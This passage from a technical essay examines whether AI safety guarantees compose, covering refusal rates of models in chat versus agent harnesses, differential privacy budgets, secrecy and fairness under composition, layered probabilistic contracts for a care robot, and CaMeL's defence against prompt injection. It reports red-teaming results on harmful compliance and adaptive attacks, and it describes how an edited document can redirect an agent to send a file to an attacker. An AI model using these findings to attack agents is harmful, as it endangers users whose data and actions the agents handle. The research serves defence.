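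Suppose a supplier guarantees that a language model rarely complies with harmful requests. The guarantee's list of assumptions might cover the model version, the languages, the system prompt, the available tools and the number of attempts a user can make. It would also have to state whether "complies" refers to what the model writes or to what it does with its tools. Ariane's limit of 32,767 followed directly from its code, but nobody can yet read the corresponding limits from a language model's weights, so developers have to look for them by experiment. One obvious assumption to examine is that the model is used as a chatbot, since developers have done much of their refusal training and testing in chat.

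### Does refusal in chat carry over to agents?

An early warning came from 2024 experiments in *Aligned LLMs Are Not Aligned Browser Agents* (Kumar, Lau and colleagues, 2025), which compared chat models with agents that operate a web browser. The researchers wrote 100 harmful tasks, each in a chat version and a browser version. GPT-4o attempted 12% of them in chat and 74% as a browser agent. Safety dropped least for Claude 3 Opus and Llama 3.1, which attempted 11% and 10% as browser agents. All these models are now long out of date.

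A more tightly controlled successor appeared in October 2026. Lee, Sriram and Erichson (2026), in *Do AI-for-Science Agents Preserve Model Safety?*, took four GPT models and placed each in five harnesses, the prompts and software that turn a model into an agent. They sent the same 50 harmful chemistry requests, with unchanged wording, to each model with and without a harness. They made each request three times and counted it if any of the three answers was harmful. The resulting rates of harmful compliance were:

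| System | GPT-5.2 | GPT-5.5 | GPT-5.6-Luna | GPT-6-Luna |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Model alone | 2% | 4% | 10% | 4% |
| In STELLA | 2% | 4% | 8% | 2% |
| In CACTUS | 4% | 8% | 14% | 2% |
| In ChemToolAgent | 20% | 8% | 10% | 4% |
| In Biomni | 24% | 14% | 8% | 4% |
| In DrugAgent | 72% | 50% | 28% | 4% |

Each request accounts for two percentage points, so many of the differences are too small to mean much. The large ones are clear, although another language model, GPT-5.5, judged which answers were harmful. GPT-5.2 gave one harmful answer in 50 requests on its own, 36 in DrugAgent, and one in STELLA. An integrator who had tested only GPT-5.2 on its own could not have known which result to expect.

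On direct requests, GPT-6-Luna, the newest of the four models, did no worse in any harness than alone. That is good evidence that the problem is not inherent in agents, but only for direct requests. An adaptive attack succeeded against GPT-6-Luna 2% of the time alone and 8% to 30% of the time in the harnesses. For GPT-5.5, the figures were 2% and 38% to 60%. The harness did not always make things worse, since the attack succeeded against GPT-5.2 56% of the time alone and 36% of the time in CACTUS. Lee and colleagues ran the adaptive attack only once per system.

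A model may also give few harmful answers for reasons other than refusal. GPT-6-Luna explicitly refused 46% of the direct requests when used alone and 9% in DrugAgent, yet few of its answers were harmful in either case. Some of the answers that weren't explicit refusals may have been harmless because they were incomplete or technically wrong. If so, a more capable successor could give more harmful answers.

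The experimenters could not identify what in a harness causes the change. When they switched off the tools or the memory in two harnesses and repeated the adaptive attack, no rate moved by more than six points. Nobody therefore knows yet which assumption about the harness to document. After flight 501, by contrast, investigators recovered both inertial units from the debris and read the circumstances of the failure from the units' memory.

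An agent's actions need to be measured separately from its text. *Behavior Beyond Text* (Gupta, Saha and colleagues, 2026) tested five open-weight models on matched requests, first in plain chat and then with tools available. Of the harmful requests that a model refused in chat, between 10% (Command R 7B) and 52% (Qwen3-14B) led to a forbidden tool call. These two models had refused similar shares in chat, 67% and 75%, so the chat score predicted the difference poorly. The requests were also worded differently when tools were available, so the tools may not be the whole cause. A system prompt with safety reminders reduced the figure from 25% to 3% for Gemma 3 27B, but only from 63% to 39% for Qwen3-14B. *Mind the GAP* (Cartagena and Teixeira, 2026) found that all six frontier models it tested sometimes refused in words while making the forbidden call.

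None of these comparisons isolates the training itself. In *Before Retrieval Begins*, Nawal, Baser and Gurusamy (2026) trained seven small open-weight models on written refusals of 80 harmful requests and on 80 harmless examples. The training data contained no tool calls. They then counted how often each model fetched a web page to help with a different set of harmful requests. In three models the rate fell by 20, 55 and 62 percentage points, while the models still fetched pages for at least 95% of harmless requests. Refusal training in text can therefore carry over to actions, though some harmful calls remained. The results for the other four models were inconclusive. Two of them, for example, stopped using the tool even for harmless requests, so their lower harmful rate doesn't show that they can tell harmful requests from harmless ones. Nawal and colleagues trained each model only once,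 so they treat the result as a pilot.

On this evidence, a supplier of GPT-6-Luna could list the five harnesses, the 50 requests and the measured rates. The list would be of some use to an integrator who uses one of those harnesses for similar work. Velocities lie on a scale, so an engineer can check a trajectory against a velocity limit even if no rocket has flown it. Harnesses do not lie on such a scale, so an integrator who builds a sixth would not know whether it falls inside the validated range.

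## Differential privacy: a guarantee defined so that it adds up

Differential privacy gives each module that handles personal data a number, ε (epsilon), which limits how much the module reveals about any one person. The numbers for several modules add up to a limit for the whole system, so privacy engineers can calculate the limit for a new combination of modules before anyone tests it. Large technology companies and the US Census Bureau have deployed differential privacy successfully, according to the US standards agency NIST.

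### The definition

Suppose a hospital lets an AI agent ask how many of its patients have diabetes. If the exact answer is 412 the day before Maria arrives and 413 the day after, and no other patients come or go, anyone who sees both answers can tell that she has diabetes. The hospital can prevent this by adding random noise to each answer.

Let M be the program that answers, and let D and D′ be two databases that differ in one person's record. M is (ε, δ)-differentially private if, for every such pair and every set S of possible answers,

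P(M(D) is in S) ≤ e^ε × P(M(D′) is in S) + δ.

We assume for now that δ is zero. At ε = 0.1, e^ε is about 1.105, so any answer is at most about 10.5% more likely with Maria's record in the database than without it. Someone who thought there was a 50% chance that her record was there could be at most 52.5% sure after seeing the answer. That limit rises to 73% at ε = 1 and to 99.995% at ε = 10, where there is hardly any protection.

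For a count, the hospital can meet the definition exactly. One record changes the true count by at most one. If the hospital adds noise x drawn with a probability density proportional to e^(−ε|x|), changing the true count by one changes the probability density of any published result by at most a factor of e^ε. At ε = 0.1, the noise moves the count up or down by about 10 patients on average. An error of that size matters little for a count of 412 but makes a count of 4 useless.

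Later processing cannot weaken the guarantee as long as it does not use the records again. If a language model turns the noisy count into a paragraph, the paragraph will mention a rise in cases, or have any other given property, only for a particular set of counts, and the inequality already covers every set. If the model also makes random choices, the same argument applies to each possible outcome of those choices. The module therefore needs no contract with later components, and its guarantee holds even against a hostile reader with other databases and unlimited computing power.

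### Why the losses add

Now suppose the agent asks two questions, and the hospital answers them with losses of ε₁ and ε₂. The probability of seeing answers a₁ and a₂ is the probability of the first times the probability of the second given the first:

P(a₁, a₂ | D) = P(a₁ | D) × P(a₂ | D, a₁)

≤ e^ε₁ P(a₁ | D′) × e^ε₂ P(a₂ | D′, a₁)

= e^(ε₁ + ε₂) P(a₁, a₂ | D′).

The pair of answers is therefore private with a loss of ε₁ + ε₂. Repeating the step shows that the total loss for ten questions, each with ε = 0.1, is at most 1. If δ is not zero, the δ values add as well. *The Composition Theorem for Differential Privacy* (2013) describes mechanisms whose loss exceeds any total smaller than the sum, so in general a smaller total requires accepting a larger δ.

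In the second factor, the first answer is already fixed, so the agent or an attacker may choose the second question after reading the first answer. This matters for language model agents, which constantly decide what to do next based on what they have just read.

The proof holds only if the second answer is private whatever the first one was. Suppose one module publishes the count plus noise, and another publishes that same noise. Alone, the second output is a random number that reveals nothing about any patient, so its ε is zero. But subtracting it from the first output gives the exact count. Drawing fresh noise for every answer prevents this, and an engineer can check from the design that the modules do so.

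### A cheaper bound for many questions

Adding up the worst case for every answer is pessimistic when there are many of them, because the noise will sometimes happen to favour one database and sometimes the other. In 2010 Dwork, Rothblum and Vadhan proved a bound that takes advantage of this. For k answers, each with loss ε, the total loss is at most

ε′ = ε√(2k ln(1/δ′)) + kε(e^ε − 1),

at the price of adding δ′ to the total δ. For 1,000 answers at ε = 0.01, the simple sum is 10. With δ′ set to one in a million, the advanced bound is about 1.76. For ten answers at ε = 0.1, the same formula gives 1.77, which is worse than the simple sum of 1.

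Roughly, δ is the probability that the guarantee set by ε fails, and it has to be very small. A program that picks one of n patients at random and publishes their full record meets the definition with ε = 0 and δ = 1/n. In a hospital with 1,000 patients, a δ of 1/1,000 would therefore allow a program that exposes one patient's record every time it runs.

### Keeping accounts for an agent

Because losses add, a system can track how much ε it has used. *Probabilistic Couplings for Probabilistic Reasoning* (2017) describes this as a running total that starts at zero. The hospital sets a limit, adds the ε of each answer to the total, and stops answering when the total reaches the limit.

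*Privacy Protection in Self-Evolving Personal Agents* (2026) works out such a budget for an agent that writes new prompts from private records. The agent may write four candidate prompts, with at most eight private attempts each. Each attempt uses ε = 0.025, so the 32 attempts together use at most 0.8. Failed attempts and retries count too, because a discarded draft still depended on the private records and its failure may influence what the agent does next.

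Many systems account for much less than this. Zhang (2026), in *From One Query to Many*, reviewed systems that answer questions from private documents and found that several state their guarantee for a single answer. The table uses reported budgets of about 10 to compare three approaches:

| Approach | Limit on ε after 1 answer | After 100 answers | Price |
|---|---|---|---|
| Protect each answer separately | 10 | 1,000 | Protection weakens with every answer |
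| Give each document its own budget, enough for one use | 10 | 10 | Useful documents drop out after one use |
| Make one private synthetic copy of the documents and use only that | 10 | 10 | Details missing from the copy are lost for every question |

The third approach relies on the rule about later processing, since no answer uses the originals again. The advanced bound doesn't help the first approach. As Zhang points out, it gives no improvement over the simple sum once the privacy loss per answer exceeds about 0.69, because its second term alone is then at least as large as that sum.

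The budget also depends on what the designers count as one record. All the systems in the review protect single documents. If a patient has twenty documents, a limit of 10 per document guarantees only a limit of 200 for the patient. And if the interface shows its sources, a retrieved document always appears when it is in the collection and never when it isn't. That forces δ up to 1, which leaves no guarantee, however small ε is.

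Privacy loss can also add up when an agent sends the same private value to several outside services. Anshumaan, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Dependency-Aware Privacy for Multi-turn LLM Agents*, consider a medical agent that sends a patient's blood sugar reading to two services and adds fresh noise each time. If the services combine the readings they receive, the privacy loss is 2ε. Their system, RootGuard, adds noise to each private value once, stores the result, and calculates everything else from the stored values. Body mass index, for example, is calculated from the noisy height and weight, so sharing it adds no privacy loss. In simulated attacks on an agent that added fresh noise each time, the error in the attacker's estimate of the private values fell from 21.8% after one request to 6.2% after 16. With RootGuard, further requests did not help the attacker. The guarantee covers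 only values that the agent recognises as private, and Anshumaan and colleagues assume that it recognises all of them.

*Agents That Know Too Much* (2026), a survey of privacy in language model agents, still lists accounting for privacy loss over a whole multi-step session as an open problem. The losses are easy to add up, but it is hard to make sure the total includes every tool call, log and displayed source.

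### What the account leaves out

The limit ε holds only because someone designed each module to respect it, whereas a physical law limits the mass leaving a vessel. Even then, ε limits only what outsiders learn because one person's data was included. A differentially private health survey can still establish that smoking causes cancer, and an insurer can use that result against a smoker who never took part.

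Privacy accounting also does not measure whether an action is harmful. If the mail assistant pays a fraudster using an account number from the fraudster's own email, the payment need not depend on any protected record, so its ε can be zero. A legitimate payment cannot have a small ε, because the bank must receive one supplier's exact account number. To control payments, engineers need other tools, such as tracking where each piece of data came from.

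### Two secret-keeping systems that leak when connected

Security properties do not normally compose. Goguen and Meseguer defined noninterference, a strict form of secrecy, for deterministic systems. It requires that deleting all the secret inputs leave the public outputs unchanged. Many real systems can respond to the same input in several ways, so researchers needed a broader version. One candidate, deducibility security, requires that someone who sees only the public messages can never rule out any sequence of secret inputs.

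Such properties can fail when two systems that have them are connected, as McCullough showed in *Noninterference and the composability of security properties* (1988). He was also a co-author of *Romulus, a Computer Security Properties Modeling Environment* (Brackin, Foley and colleagues, 1996), which gives a small example:

- System A receives secret messages and can also send its own at any time. At some point it publicly announces "stop", followed by "odd" or "even", depending on how many secret messages it has received and sent. An observer who reads "odd" learns nothing about the inputs, because A could have sent an extra message that changed the result.
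- System B works in the same way, except that it receives "stop" instead of announcing it.
- An engineer connects the two, so that each one's secret messages go to the other and A's "stop" goes to B.

Both systems now count every message that passes between them. If nobody outside sends a secret message, the two totals match, and A and B announce the same word. If they exchange three messages and an outsider sends one more to A, A announces "even" and B announces "odd", so the observer can tell that someone sent a secret message. A's own messages were the noise that hid its secret inputs, but B counted those messages too, so comparing the two announcements removes the noise. The hospital's count would leak in the same way if a second module published the noise.

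The inductive argument that works for safety properties does not help here. An engineer can tell from a single run whether a confidential file left the company, but not whether an observer could have inferred a secret, because that depends on what else the system might have done. McLean, in *A General Theory of Composition for Trace Sets*, explains that many secrecy properties fall outside Abadi and Lamport's method for this reason. He found that one broad version of noninterference still holds when systems form a one-way chain but can fail when they feed back into each other, as the parts of an agent often do.

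To fix this, McCullough proposed a stronger property called restrictiveness. Among other things, it requires that a secret input arriving just before a public one leave the public behaviour unchanged. System B violates this because a secret message just before "stop" changes "odd" to "even". Brackin and colleagues prove that connecting two restrictive systems produces another. However, programmers cannot assume that their tools enforce such a strong property. Rafnsson and Sabelfeld showed in *Compositional Information-flow Security for Interactive Systems* that the condition behind several practical tools can fail when secure programs run side by side.

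### Fair classifiers in an unfair system

Cynthia Dwork, one of the inventors of differential privacy, later looked for similar rules about fairness and found that fair classifiers do not always combine into a fair system. *Fairness Under Composition* (Dwork and Ilvento, 2018) calls a classifier fair if it gives similar people similar chances, where "similar" depends on the task. For a job advertisement it might mean similar qualifications, and for a grocery advertisement a similar interest in grocery delivery.

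Suppose two equally qualified people, Ana and Ben, visit a web page with space for one advertisement. The job advertiser always bids for both of them. The grocery advertiser bids for Ana 80% of the time and for Ben 20%, because Ana is much more likely to order groceries. Each advertiser is fair by the standard of its own task. But the grocery advertiser pays more and wins whenever it bids, so Ana sees the job advertisement 20% of the time and Ben sees it 80%.

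Changing the rule for who wins the ad space does not solve the problem in general. Dwork and Ilvento prove that, for any two tasks with non-trivial standards of similarity and any such rule, some pair of fair classifiers produces an unfair result. The two advertisers compare people by different standards, so a difference that is legitimate for grocery ads can also affect who sees job ads. Differential privacy avoids this problem because every module uses the same comparison. Each one limits how much its output probabilities can differ between a database with one person's record and the same database without it.

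Dwork and Ilvento also give a fix that doesn't change the classifiers. The page first picks a task at random, with the same odds for everyone, then runs only that task's classifier. With even odds, Ana and Ben each see the job advertisement half the time. However, the space sometimes stays empty when the other advertiser would have paid for it.

### Protocols that stay secure in any surroundings

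Cryptographers have defined a much broader kind of security that composes. Their early definitions considered only a single run of a protocol, and some protocols that met them became insecure when two runs overlapped. *Universally Composable Security* (Canetti, 2001) defines security using a test that includes the protocol's surroundings, such as other protocols running at the same time.

The designer describes an ideal version of the task, in which everyone gives their inputs to a perfectly trustworthy party, who computes and returns the results. In a sealed-bid auction, this party would collect the bids and announce only the winner and the price. The real protocol has no such party. It passes the test if, for every attacker on the real protocol, some attacker on the ideal version can make the two look the same to any outside program. This program, called the environment, represents everything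 else on the network. It chooses the inputs, sees the outputs and can exchange information with the attacker at any time during the run.

Canetti proved that a protocol that passes the test remains secure as part of any larger system, even when it runs alongside an unlimited number of other protocols controlled by an attacker. Engineers can therefore design the larger system as if the trustworthy party existed, then replace that party with the real protocol.

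This strength depends on assumptions about the attacker and the set-up. *Universally Composable Two-Party and Multi-Party Secure Computation* (Canetti, Lindell and colleagues, 2002) shows how to build such protocols for a very wide range of tasks, but it assumes that certain mathematical problems are too hard for the attacker to solve. It also assumes a common reference string, which is random data that all participants share and nobody has rigged. Cryptographers have since proved that many two-party tasks require some set-up of this kind.

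The method also needs an exact description of the ideal version. It is feasible to write one for an auction. But for an assistant that reads email and pays invoices, the trustworthy party would have to know which payments the company wants to make, and nobody has written a program that specifies this.

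## A three-layer contract design for language model agents

Developers can rarely guarantee what a language model will do, but they can state how often a guarantee holds. A probabilistic contract adds a probability to the usual assumption and guarantee, for example "if an authorised person made the request, the plan breaks no house rule at least 95% of the time". In May 2026 Bensalem and colleagues proposed deriving the safety of a whole agent from three such contracts, one for each layer of checks. They ran no experiments and instead support the proposal with arithmetic and an argument about when each check becomes possible.

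### Three layers around a care robot

The paper's example is a robot in a home for elderly people. A caregiver asks it to visit Rooms 12, 15 and 18 before 15:00, check that the residents are well and drinking enough, bring water if needed, and not disturb anyone during rest periods. A language model turns the request into a plan, which passes through the layers in order.

The user layer checks the plan before the robot observes anything. It confirms that the caregiver is allowed to give such orders, and compares the plan with the request, the house rules and ethical constraints. It would reject a plan that left out the water, sent the robot into a room during rest hours without permission, or sent it through a bathroom with its cameras on.

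The operational layer uses sensor data to check whether the robot is within its operational design domain, the full set of situations for which it is certified. Room 15 is closed for a clinical procedure, so the layer drops that visit and notifies the caregiver. The corridor to Room 12 is dim but within the domain, so the layer allows the trip with a speed limit.

The functional layer controls the robot as it moves. It stops the robot when a resident steps into the corridor, and limits the force of the arm as it hands over a glass. It uses tools such as a control barrier function, which changes a movement command by the smallest amount that keeps the robot inside a calculated safe region. When moved furniture blocks the delivery point in Room 18, the functional layer reports this upwards so that the user layer can make a new plan.

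Each layer assumes what the previous layer guarantees. The functional layer, for instance, assumes that the robot is inside its certified domain and under the speed limit. Limits like these are easier to combine than probabilities. If the layers set different speed limits, a robot that obeys the lowest one obeys them all.

### Four formulas for the whole system

Let U, O and F be the events that the user, operational and functional layers meet their guarantees. Bensalem and colleagues count the system as safe when all three events occur, and give four formulas for the probability that they do. For the robot, they assume P(U) = 95%, P(O) = 90% and P(F) = 92%.

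| | Formula | Data needed | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| B1 | P(U) + P(O) + P(F) − 2 | Each layer's success rate | 77.0% |
| B2 | B1 plus the rates at which each pair fails together | Also the three pair rates (2% each) | 83.0% |
| B3 | 1 − P(at least one layer fails) | Also the rate at which all three fail together (0.4%) | 82.6% |
| B4 | P(U) × P(O given U) × P(F given U and O) | Each layer's success rate when the earlier guarantees hold (95%, 94%, 96%) | 85.7% |

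B1 is the union bound. If the layers were independent, the result would be 0.95 × 0.90 × 0.92, or 78.7%. All the inputs are illustrative, and some are based on only distantly related evidence. For example, the operational layer's 90% is based on a benchmark in which language models missed 12% of questions outside their assigned subject, and 71% when the questions were disguised.

B2 is an upper bound on how often the system is safe, though Bensalem and colleagues present it as a lower bound. It is higher than the exact answer, B3, because it leaves out the occasions when all three layers fail at once. Adding the layers' failure rates counts each such occasion three times, and subtracting the three pair rates then removes it three times. The same data do give a valid lower bound. All three layers cannot fail together more often than any two of them do, so they fail together at most 2% of the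 time, and the system is safe at least 81% of the time.

B3 and B4 are both exact, so they should agree for any one system. They differ here because their inputs describe different systems. If P(O given U) is 94%, both guarantees hold 89.3% of the time, so the two layers must fail together 4.3% of the time, but B3 uses 2%. With the 2% and 0.4% from B3, the last two factors in B4 would be 91.6% and 94.9%, and B4 would also give 82.6%.

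The authors attribute B4's seven-point advantage over the independent figure to filtering, since the user layer may remove plans that would have caused problems later. In the formula, however, P(O given U) exceeds P(O) only if the two layers tend to succeed and fail together. For P(O given U) to be 94% when P(O) is 90%, the operational layer must also fail in 86% of the cases where the user layer fails (4.3 out of 5). An engineer would need records of both layers on the same cases to check this.

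All four formulas also leave out harm that occurs when every guarantee holds. Suppose a doctor restricts a resident's fluids and nobody updates the robot's rules. The resident may come to harm even though the plan matches the request and the known policy, the room is open, and the arm hands over the water gently.

### Does timing require three layers?

Bensalem and colleagues claim that at least three separately certified stages are needed. Their argument starts from the information a checker has at each point. Two runs can have the same plan but differ in whether Room 15 is open. A checker given only the plan must return the same result for both, so it is wrong about one of them. Two runs with the same plan in the same building can also differ because a resident steps into the corridor in only one. Some checks therefore have to wait for sensor data, and others have to continue while the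 robot moves. This part of the argument is sound, and it rules out certifying such a robot by inspecting its plans alone.

The design does not need exactly three stages. A designer could use a plan checker before departure and then a single monitor that reads all the sensors continuously and stops the robot if a room is off limits or a collision is near. The paper objects that the movement controller needs a stable verdict about the surroundings, issued before it starts, to serve as its assumption. But that need comes from how the paper writes the contract between the second and third layers, and none of the three starting requirements includes it. The paper's operational layer also keeps checking during execution, as it must if a room can close while the robot is on its way.

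Bensalem and colleagues also count a single component that carries out all three checks in sequence as a three-layer design with hidden boundaries. A working two-part robot would therefore not refute their claim, because they could always say that the third layer is inside one of its parts.

The number of layers also depends on the agent. The mail assistant has no arm to control, and it learns something new each time it opens an email, retrieves a file or hears back from the bank. Its designer could reasonably put a checkpoint at one of those moments or at ten. The claim about timing therefore supports checking facts when they become available, but the number three comes from the paper's division of the robot's work.

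There is still a good practical case for explicit stages, because engineers can test and audit each one separately, and can measure the rates in B4, which is difficult if a single component makes all the decisions internally. This doesn't prove that no other design can work.

### Where the probabilities would come from

Bensalem and colleagues describe their formulas as a target for certification, because the inputs are too hard to measure for anyone to issue a certificate today.

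One obstacle is that what the model writes earlier in a session affects what it does next, so 1,000 recorded steps from ten sessions are not 1,000 independent tests. An engineer can avoid this problem by counting whole missions, but then she needs many more of them. To show with 95% confidence that all three layers succeed at least 95% of the time, she would need 59 independent missions with no failures in any layer. If she changed the language model, she would have to run them again.

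Uncertainty also accumulates. If she knows each layer's success rate to within two points, she knows B1 only to within six points, so the 77% could be anywhere from 71% to 83%. If each of the three estimates has 95% confidence, the union bound guarantees only 85% confidence that all three are right. In B4, a four-point error in the second factor shifts the result by 3.6 points.

The last obstacle is a language model shared by several layers. One hostile prompt, or one kind of request that the model handles badly, could defeat them all at once. The paper argues that this makes the figure that assumes independent failures too cautious rather than unsafe. That is right for the paper's own formula, which treats the layers as a chain by counting the system as safe only if every layer works. However, the appendix also warns that the true risk rises as the layers fail together more often. If each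 layer's own failure rate stays fixed, this is true of back-ups, but B3 gives the opposite result.

For some harms, though, the layers back each other up. The operational layer accounts for the time of day and access restrictions, so it and the user layer should both stop the robot from entering a room during rest hours. The robot disturbs the resident only if both fail, and a shared weakness makes that more likely. Bensalem and colleagues suggest using different language models in different layers, but they note that these models share much of their training data and would all receive the same plan. They are more confident in basing the functional layer on a model of the robot's physics, which shares no parameters with the language model.

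### Agent Behavioral Contracts and a test of independence

An earlier design has been tested on real models. Bhardwaj (2026), in *Agent Behavioral Contracts*, published in February, divides an agent's rules into hard ones, which it must never break, and soft ones, which it may break briefly if it recovers. "Never reveal personal data" would be hard, and "keep a professional tone" soft. The contract has three parameters:

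- With probability at least p, the agent breaks no hard rule during the session.
- Also with probability at least p, whenever the share of soft rules it satisfies drops below 1 − δ, the share recovers within k steps.

Recovery makes a large difference over long sessions. An agent with an independent 99% chance of complying at each step has only a 37% chance of getting through 100 steps without a slip. If it repairs 95% of its slips within the allowed window, its chance of finishing with no unrepaired slip rises to at least 95%. Slips in tone can be repaired this way, but money sent to a fraudster may be gone for good, so hard rules allow no window for repair.

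As with any contracts, an engineer connecting two agents must match the first agent's guarantee to the second agent's assumption. Bhardwaj adds two conditions. The first agent must not be allowed any action that the second agent's rules forbid, and the first agent's repairs must leave the second agent's assumption true. For example, a repair in the mail assistant that shortens an overlong summary might break the second condition by deleting the contract number that the planner needs.

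Bhardwaj multiplies the success probabilities, which requires the further assumption that, once the handoff is correct, the second agent's success does not depend on what happened inside the first. If five agents each succeed 95% of the time and the four handoffs between them each succeed 98% of the time, the whole pipeline succeeds with probability at least 0.95⁵ × 0.98⁴, or 71.4%. The union bound gives 67% without assuming independence, so the extra assumption raises the lower bound by only about four percentage points.

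Bhardwaj tested the contracts in 1,980 sessions with seven models. The monitoring software detected 5.2 to 6.8 soft violations per session that went unnoticed without a contract. Depending on the model, compliance with hard rules ranged from 88% to 100%, and successful recovery from 17% to 100%. These results show that software can monitor such rules while a single agent is running, but they don't test the multiplication.

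The test of that came in August, from Bhardwaj, Singh and Bhardwaj (2026), in *Agent Behavioral Contracts II*. They gave pairs of agents 18,000 retail and financial tasks, such as applying a refund policy or checking a transaction limit, and scored the answers with ordinary code instead of another language model. The first agent always ran on Mistral Small 24B. The second ran on the same model, on a smaller one from the same company (Ministral 8B), or on one from another company (Gemma 3 12B). From their counts one can compare what independence predicts with what happened:

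| Second agent's model | Failure rates, first and second agent | Both work: predicted, measured | Both fail: predicted, measured |
|---|---|---|---|
| Same model | 39%, 37% | 38%, 60% | 15%, 36% |
| Same company | 39%, 51% | 30%, 48% | 20%, 38% |
| Another company | 38%, 37% | 39%, 58% | 14%, 33% |

In each row, both measured figures exceed the predicted ones by the covariance, which is about 22, 18 and 19 points respectively. Two copies of the same model did far better as a chain than multiplication predicts, but would have done far worse as back-ups. In February, Bhardwaj warned that a shared model would make the chain figure too optimistic. The August results show the opposite for chains but confirm the danger for back-ups.

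When at least one of the two identical models failed a task, both failed it 90% of the time. When one of the pair was replaced with a model from another company, the figure was still 79%. Bhardwaj and colleagues had expected that switching companies would reduce the dependence more than switching models alone, but they found no reliable evidence that it did. Some of the overlap may arise because the second agent worked from the first one's output, but the pattern also appeared in smaller experiments in which the agents never saw each other's work. Some tasks may also be hard for all three models. These are small models with high failure rates, so the percentages are weak evidence about the best current models.

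The August work also offers a guarantee that assumes nothing about dependence between agents. The method considers all the joint probabilities that fit the measured data, allowing for sampling error, and reports the lowest chance that every agent succeeds. Bhardwaj and colleagues tried this on 717 tasks that four agents had all attempted. The guaranteed minimum was 25% using the success rates of single agents and pairs, and 41% after adding the rates for groups of three. All four agents had in fact succeeded on 53% of the tasks, and a standard confidence bound on that count gives a minimum of about 50%. Inferring the system's reliability from its parts therefore gave a weaker guarantee than running the whole system and counting successes, and it still required data on agents attempting the same tasks.

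Statisticians often fill such gaps by fitting a standard model of dependence, but this can be worse than having no estimate. Suppose three agents each succeed 60% of the time, and both agents in any given pair succeed 46.5% of the time. The chance that all three succeed can be anything from 33.0% to 46.5%, and one common model estimates it at 39.2%. If the true figure is 33.0%, the error can't be detected from data on single agents and pairs, and collecting more of those data only narrows the confidence interval around 39.2%.

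### Attaching safety claims to components

Measured rates are of little use to an integrator who doesn't know which version of a module they describe. Zhao's *Composable Assurance for AI Alignment*, presented at the 2026 AAAI conference, proposes attaching them to components as machine-readable claims. Each claim names and defines a property, then gives the test used, the score, the test conditions and the evidence. The evidence includes a cryptographic fingerprint of the component, so nobody can apply a claim about one version of a model to another without the mismatch showing. One example records a score of 0.85 for an image classifier under a specified attack, along with the dataset and the software version. A label like this would have helped Ariane 5's engineers if it had listed the velocity limit.

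Zhao then defines rules for combining the claims, so that software can block a release that falls short of a policy. One rule covers the accuracy of a chatbot's document collection. Adding 2,000 documents that are 80% accurate to 8,000 that are 95% accurate gives 10,000 documents that are 92% accurate. This figure is exact if nobody removes duplicates, because the numbers of accurate documents add up. But it applies only to the collection as a whole. If 60% of users' questions lead to the new documents, the average accuracy of the documents behind the answers is 86%.

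Another rule concerns two models that vote. One has a robustness score of 0.8 and the other 0.6, and Zhao suggests giving the pair the lower score, 0.6, as a conservative choice. Suppose the scores are the shares of the same test inputs on which each model answers correctly under attack. The right score for the pair then depends on how the system uses the two votes:

| How the system uses the two answers | Lowest possible score | Score if independent | Highest possible score |
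|---|---|---|---|
| Both must be right | 0.4 | 0.48 | 0.6 |
| It picks one of the two at random | 0.7 | 0.7 | 0.7 |
| One right answer is enough | 0.8 | 0.92 | 1.0 |

If both models must be right, the suggested score is the best case. It is correct only if the stronger model never fails on an input that the weaker one gets right. In the worst case, the first model fails on 20% of inputs and the second fails on a different 40%, which leaves 0.4. Taking the minimum is sound for the robot's speed limits, because obeying the lowest limit means obeying the others, but not for success rates, because the models may fail on different inputs.

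A third rule makes one claim depend on others. In Zhao's example, the chatbot counts as "truthful" if its documents have an accuracy certificate and its retriever finds relevant documents often enough. Neither condition concerns the language model that writes the answer, so the chatbot would still count as "truthful" even if the model ignored the documents and invented something.

In Zhao's walkthrough, software also monitors the finished chatbot, and it avoids this problem by testing actual answers. When the measured rate of factual errors rises from 2% to 5%, the software alerts the engineers and restores the previous version. But the likely cause in the example is that users have started asking about subjects the documents don't cover, and the previous version may do no better on those.

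### What a union bound can add up

A rule for combining claims has to fit the type of guarantee as well as the way the parts are joined. *Reliable Agentic Data Systems* (Zhang, 2026) explains how guarantees differ for agents that query databases. Suppose an agent asks how many accounts were reachable from a given account in March, and the database returns the first 100 rows and reports an exact total of 343. Software can verify the statement "343 accounts" and reject "100 accounts". If 12 of the 100 rows are in Ohio, it can verify only that the total in Ohio is between 12 and 255, because any number of the 243 missing rows could be there too.

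These are guarantees about a particular answer. A statistical guarantee, such as "at most 5% of answers are wrong", applies to a whole population of requests and gives little assurance about any one of them. Zhang warns that people often confuse the two and so claim too much.

The union bound can still add population guarantees, such as limits on how often the planner misreads a request and how often the answer-writing model makes an unsupported statement. The sum assumes that the database between the two components executes queries correctly and that both rates apply to all requests.

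The sum does not limit the error rate among the answers that users see. Suppose a system makes errors on 5% of all requests but releases only 20% of its answers, withholding the rest as too uncertain. All the errors could be among the released answers, and 25% of those would then be wrong. A developer who wants to limit the error rate among released answers has to calibrate the release rule for that purpose.

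The union bound also doesn't account for how the sizes of errors combine. Suppose one module estimates a company's revenue at $1,000,000 and another estimates its costs at $980,000, each within 1% of the truth at least 95% of the time. By the union bound, both are within 1% at least 90% of the time. The agent then reports a profit of $20,000, but even when both estimates are that accurate, the true profit could be anywhere from about $200 to nearly $40,000. To bound the error in the final result, an engineer has to track the errors in the estimates through each calculation.

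Any such sum also depends on who decided which answers were wrong. Zhang cites an experiment with systems that translate questions into database queries. Their developers had used automatic checks of the query results to calibrate them to a 10% risk of error. When experts judged the same kind of output, the risk was between 17% and 20%. If two stages were each calibrated to 10% but had a real risk of 20%, the sum would give a maximum error rate of 20% when the real maximum was 40%.

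Zhang therefore prefers deterministic checks wherever possible, designed to err only by rejecting sound answers. If each check never approves an unsound answer, the checks together never will either, whether or not their mistakes are correlated. This holds only if other components supply the checks with accurate information. No check inside the database can establish that the query matched what the user meant. The checks may also reject many answers, and a system that never answers would meet the standard, so Zhang recommends that developers report the share of requests answered alongside the rate of unsupported claims.

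## CaMeL: enforcing data-flow rules outside the model

The mail assistant's planner relies on its input containing no instructions from strangers, but a faithful copy of an email can include them. Training can make a planner follow such instructions less often, but can't guarantee that it never will. CaMeL, a 2025 design from Google DeepMind by Debenedetti and colleagues, keeps these instructions out of the planner's input by never passing it the email. Ordinary software then controls where the email's contents can go.

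### One request, step by step

CaMeL builds on a design that Simon Willison published in 2023. One language model plans and can use tools, but it sees only the user's request. A second, quarantined model reads untrusted text but cannot call tools. As Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Debenedetti and colleagues found a gap in this design. If the plan is to send a file to an email address that the quarantined model finds in a document, anyone who can edit the document can change the address, and the unchanged plan then sends the file to the attacker.

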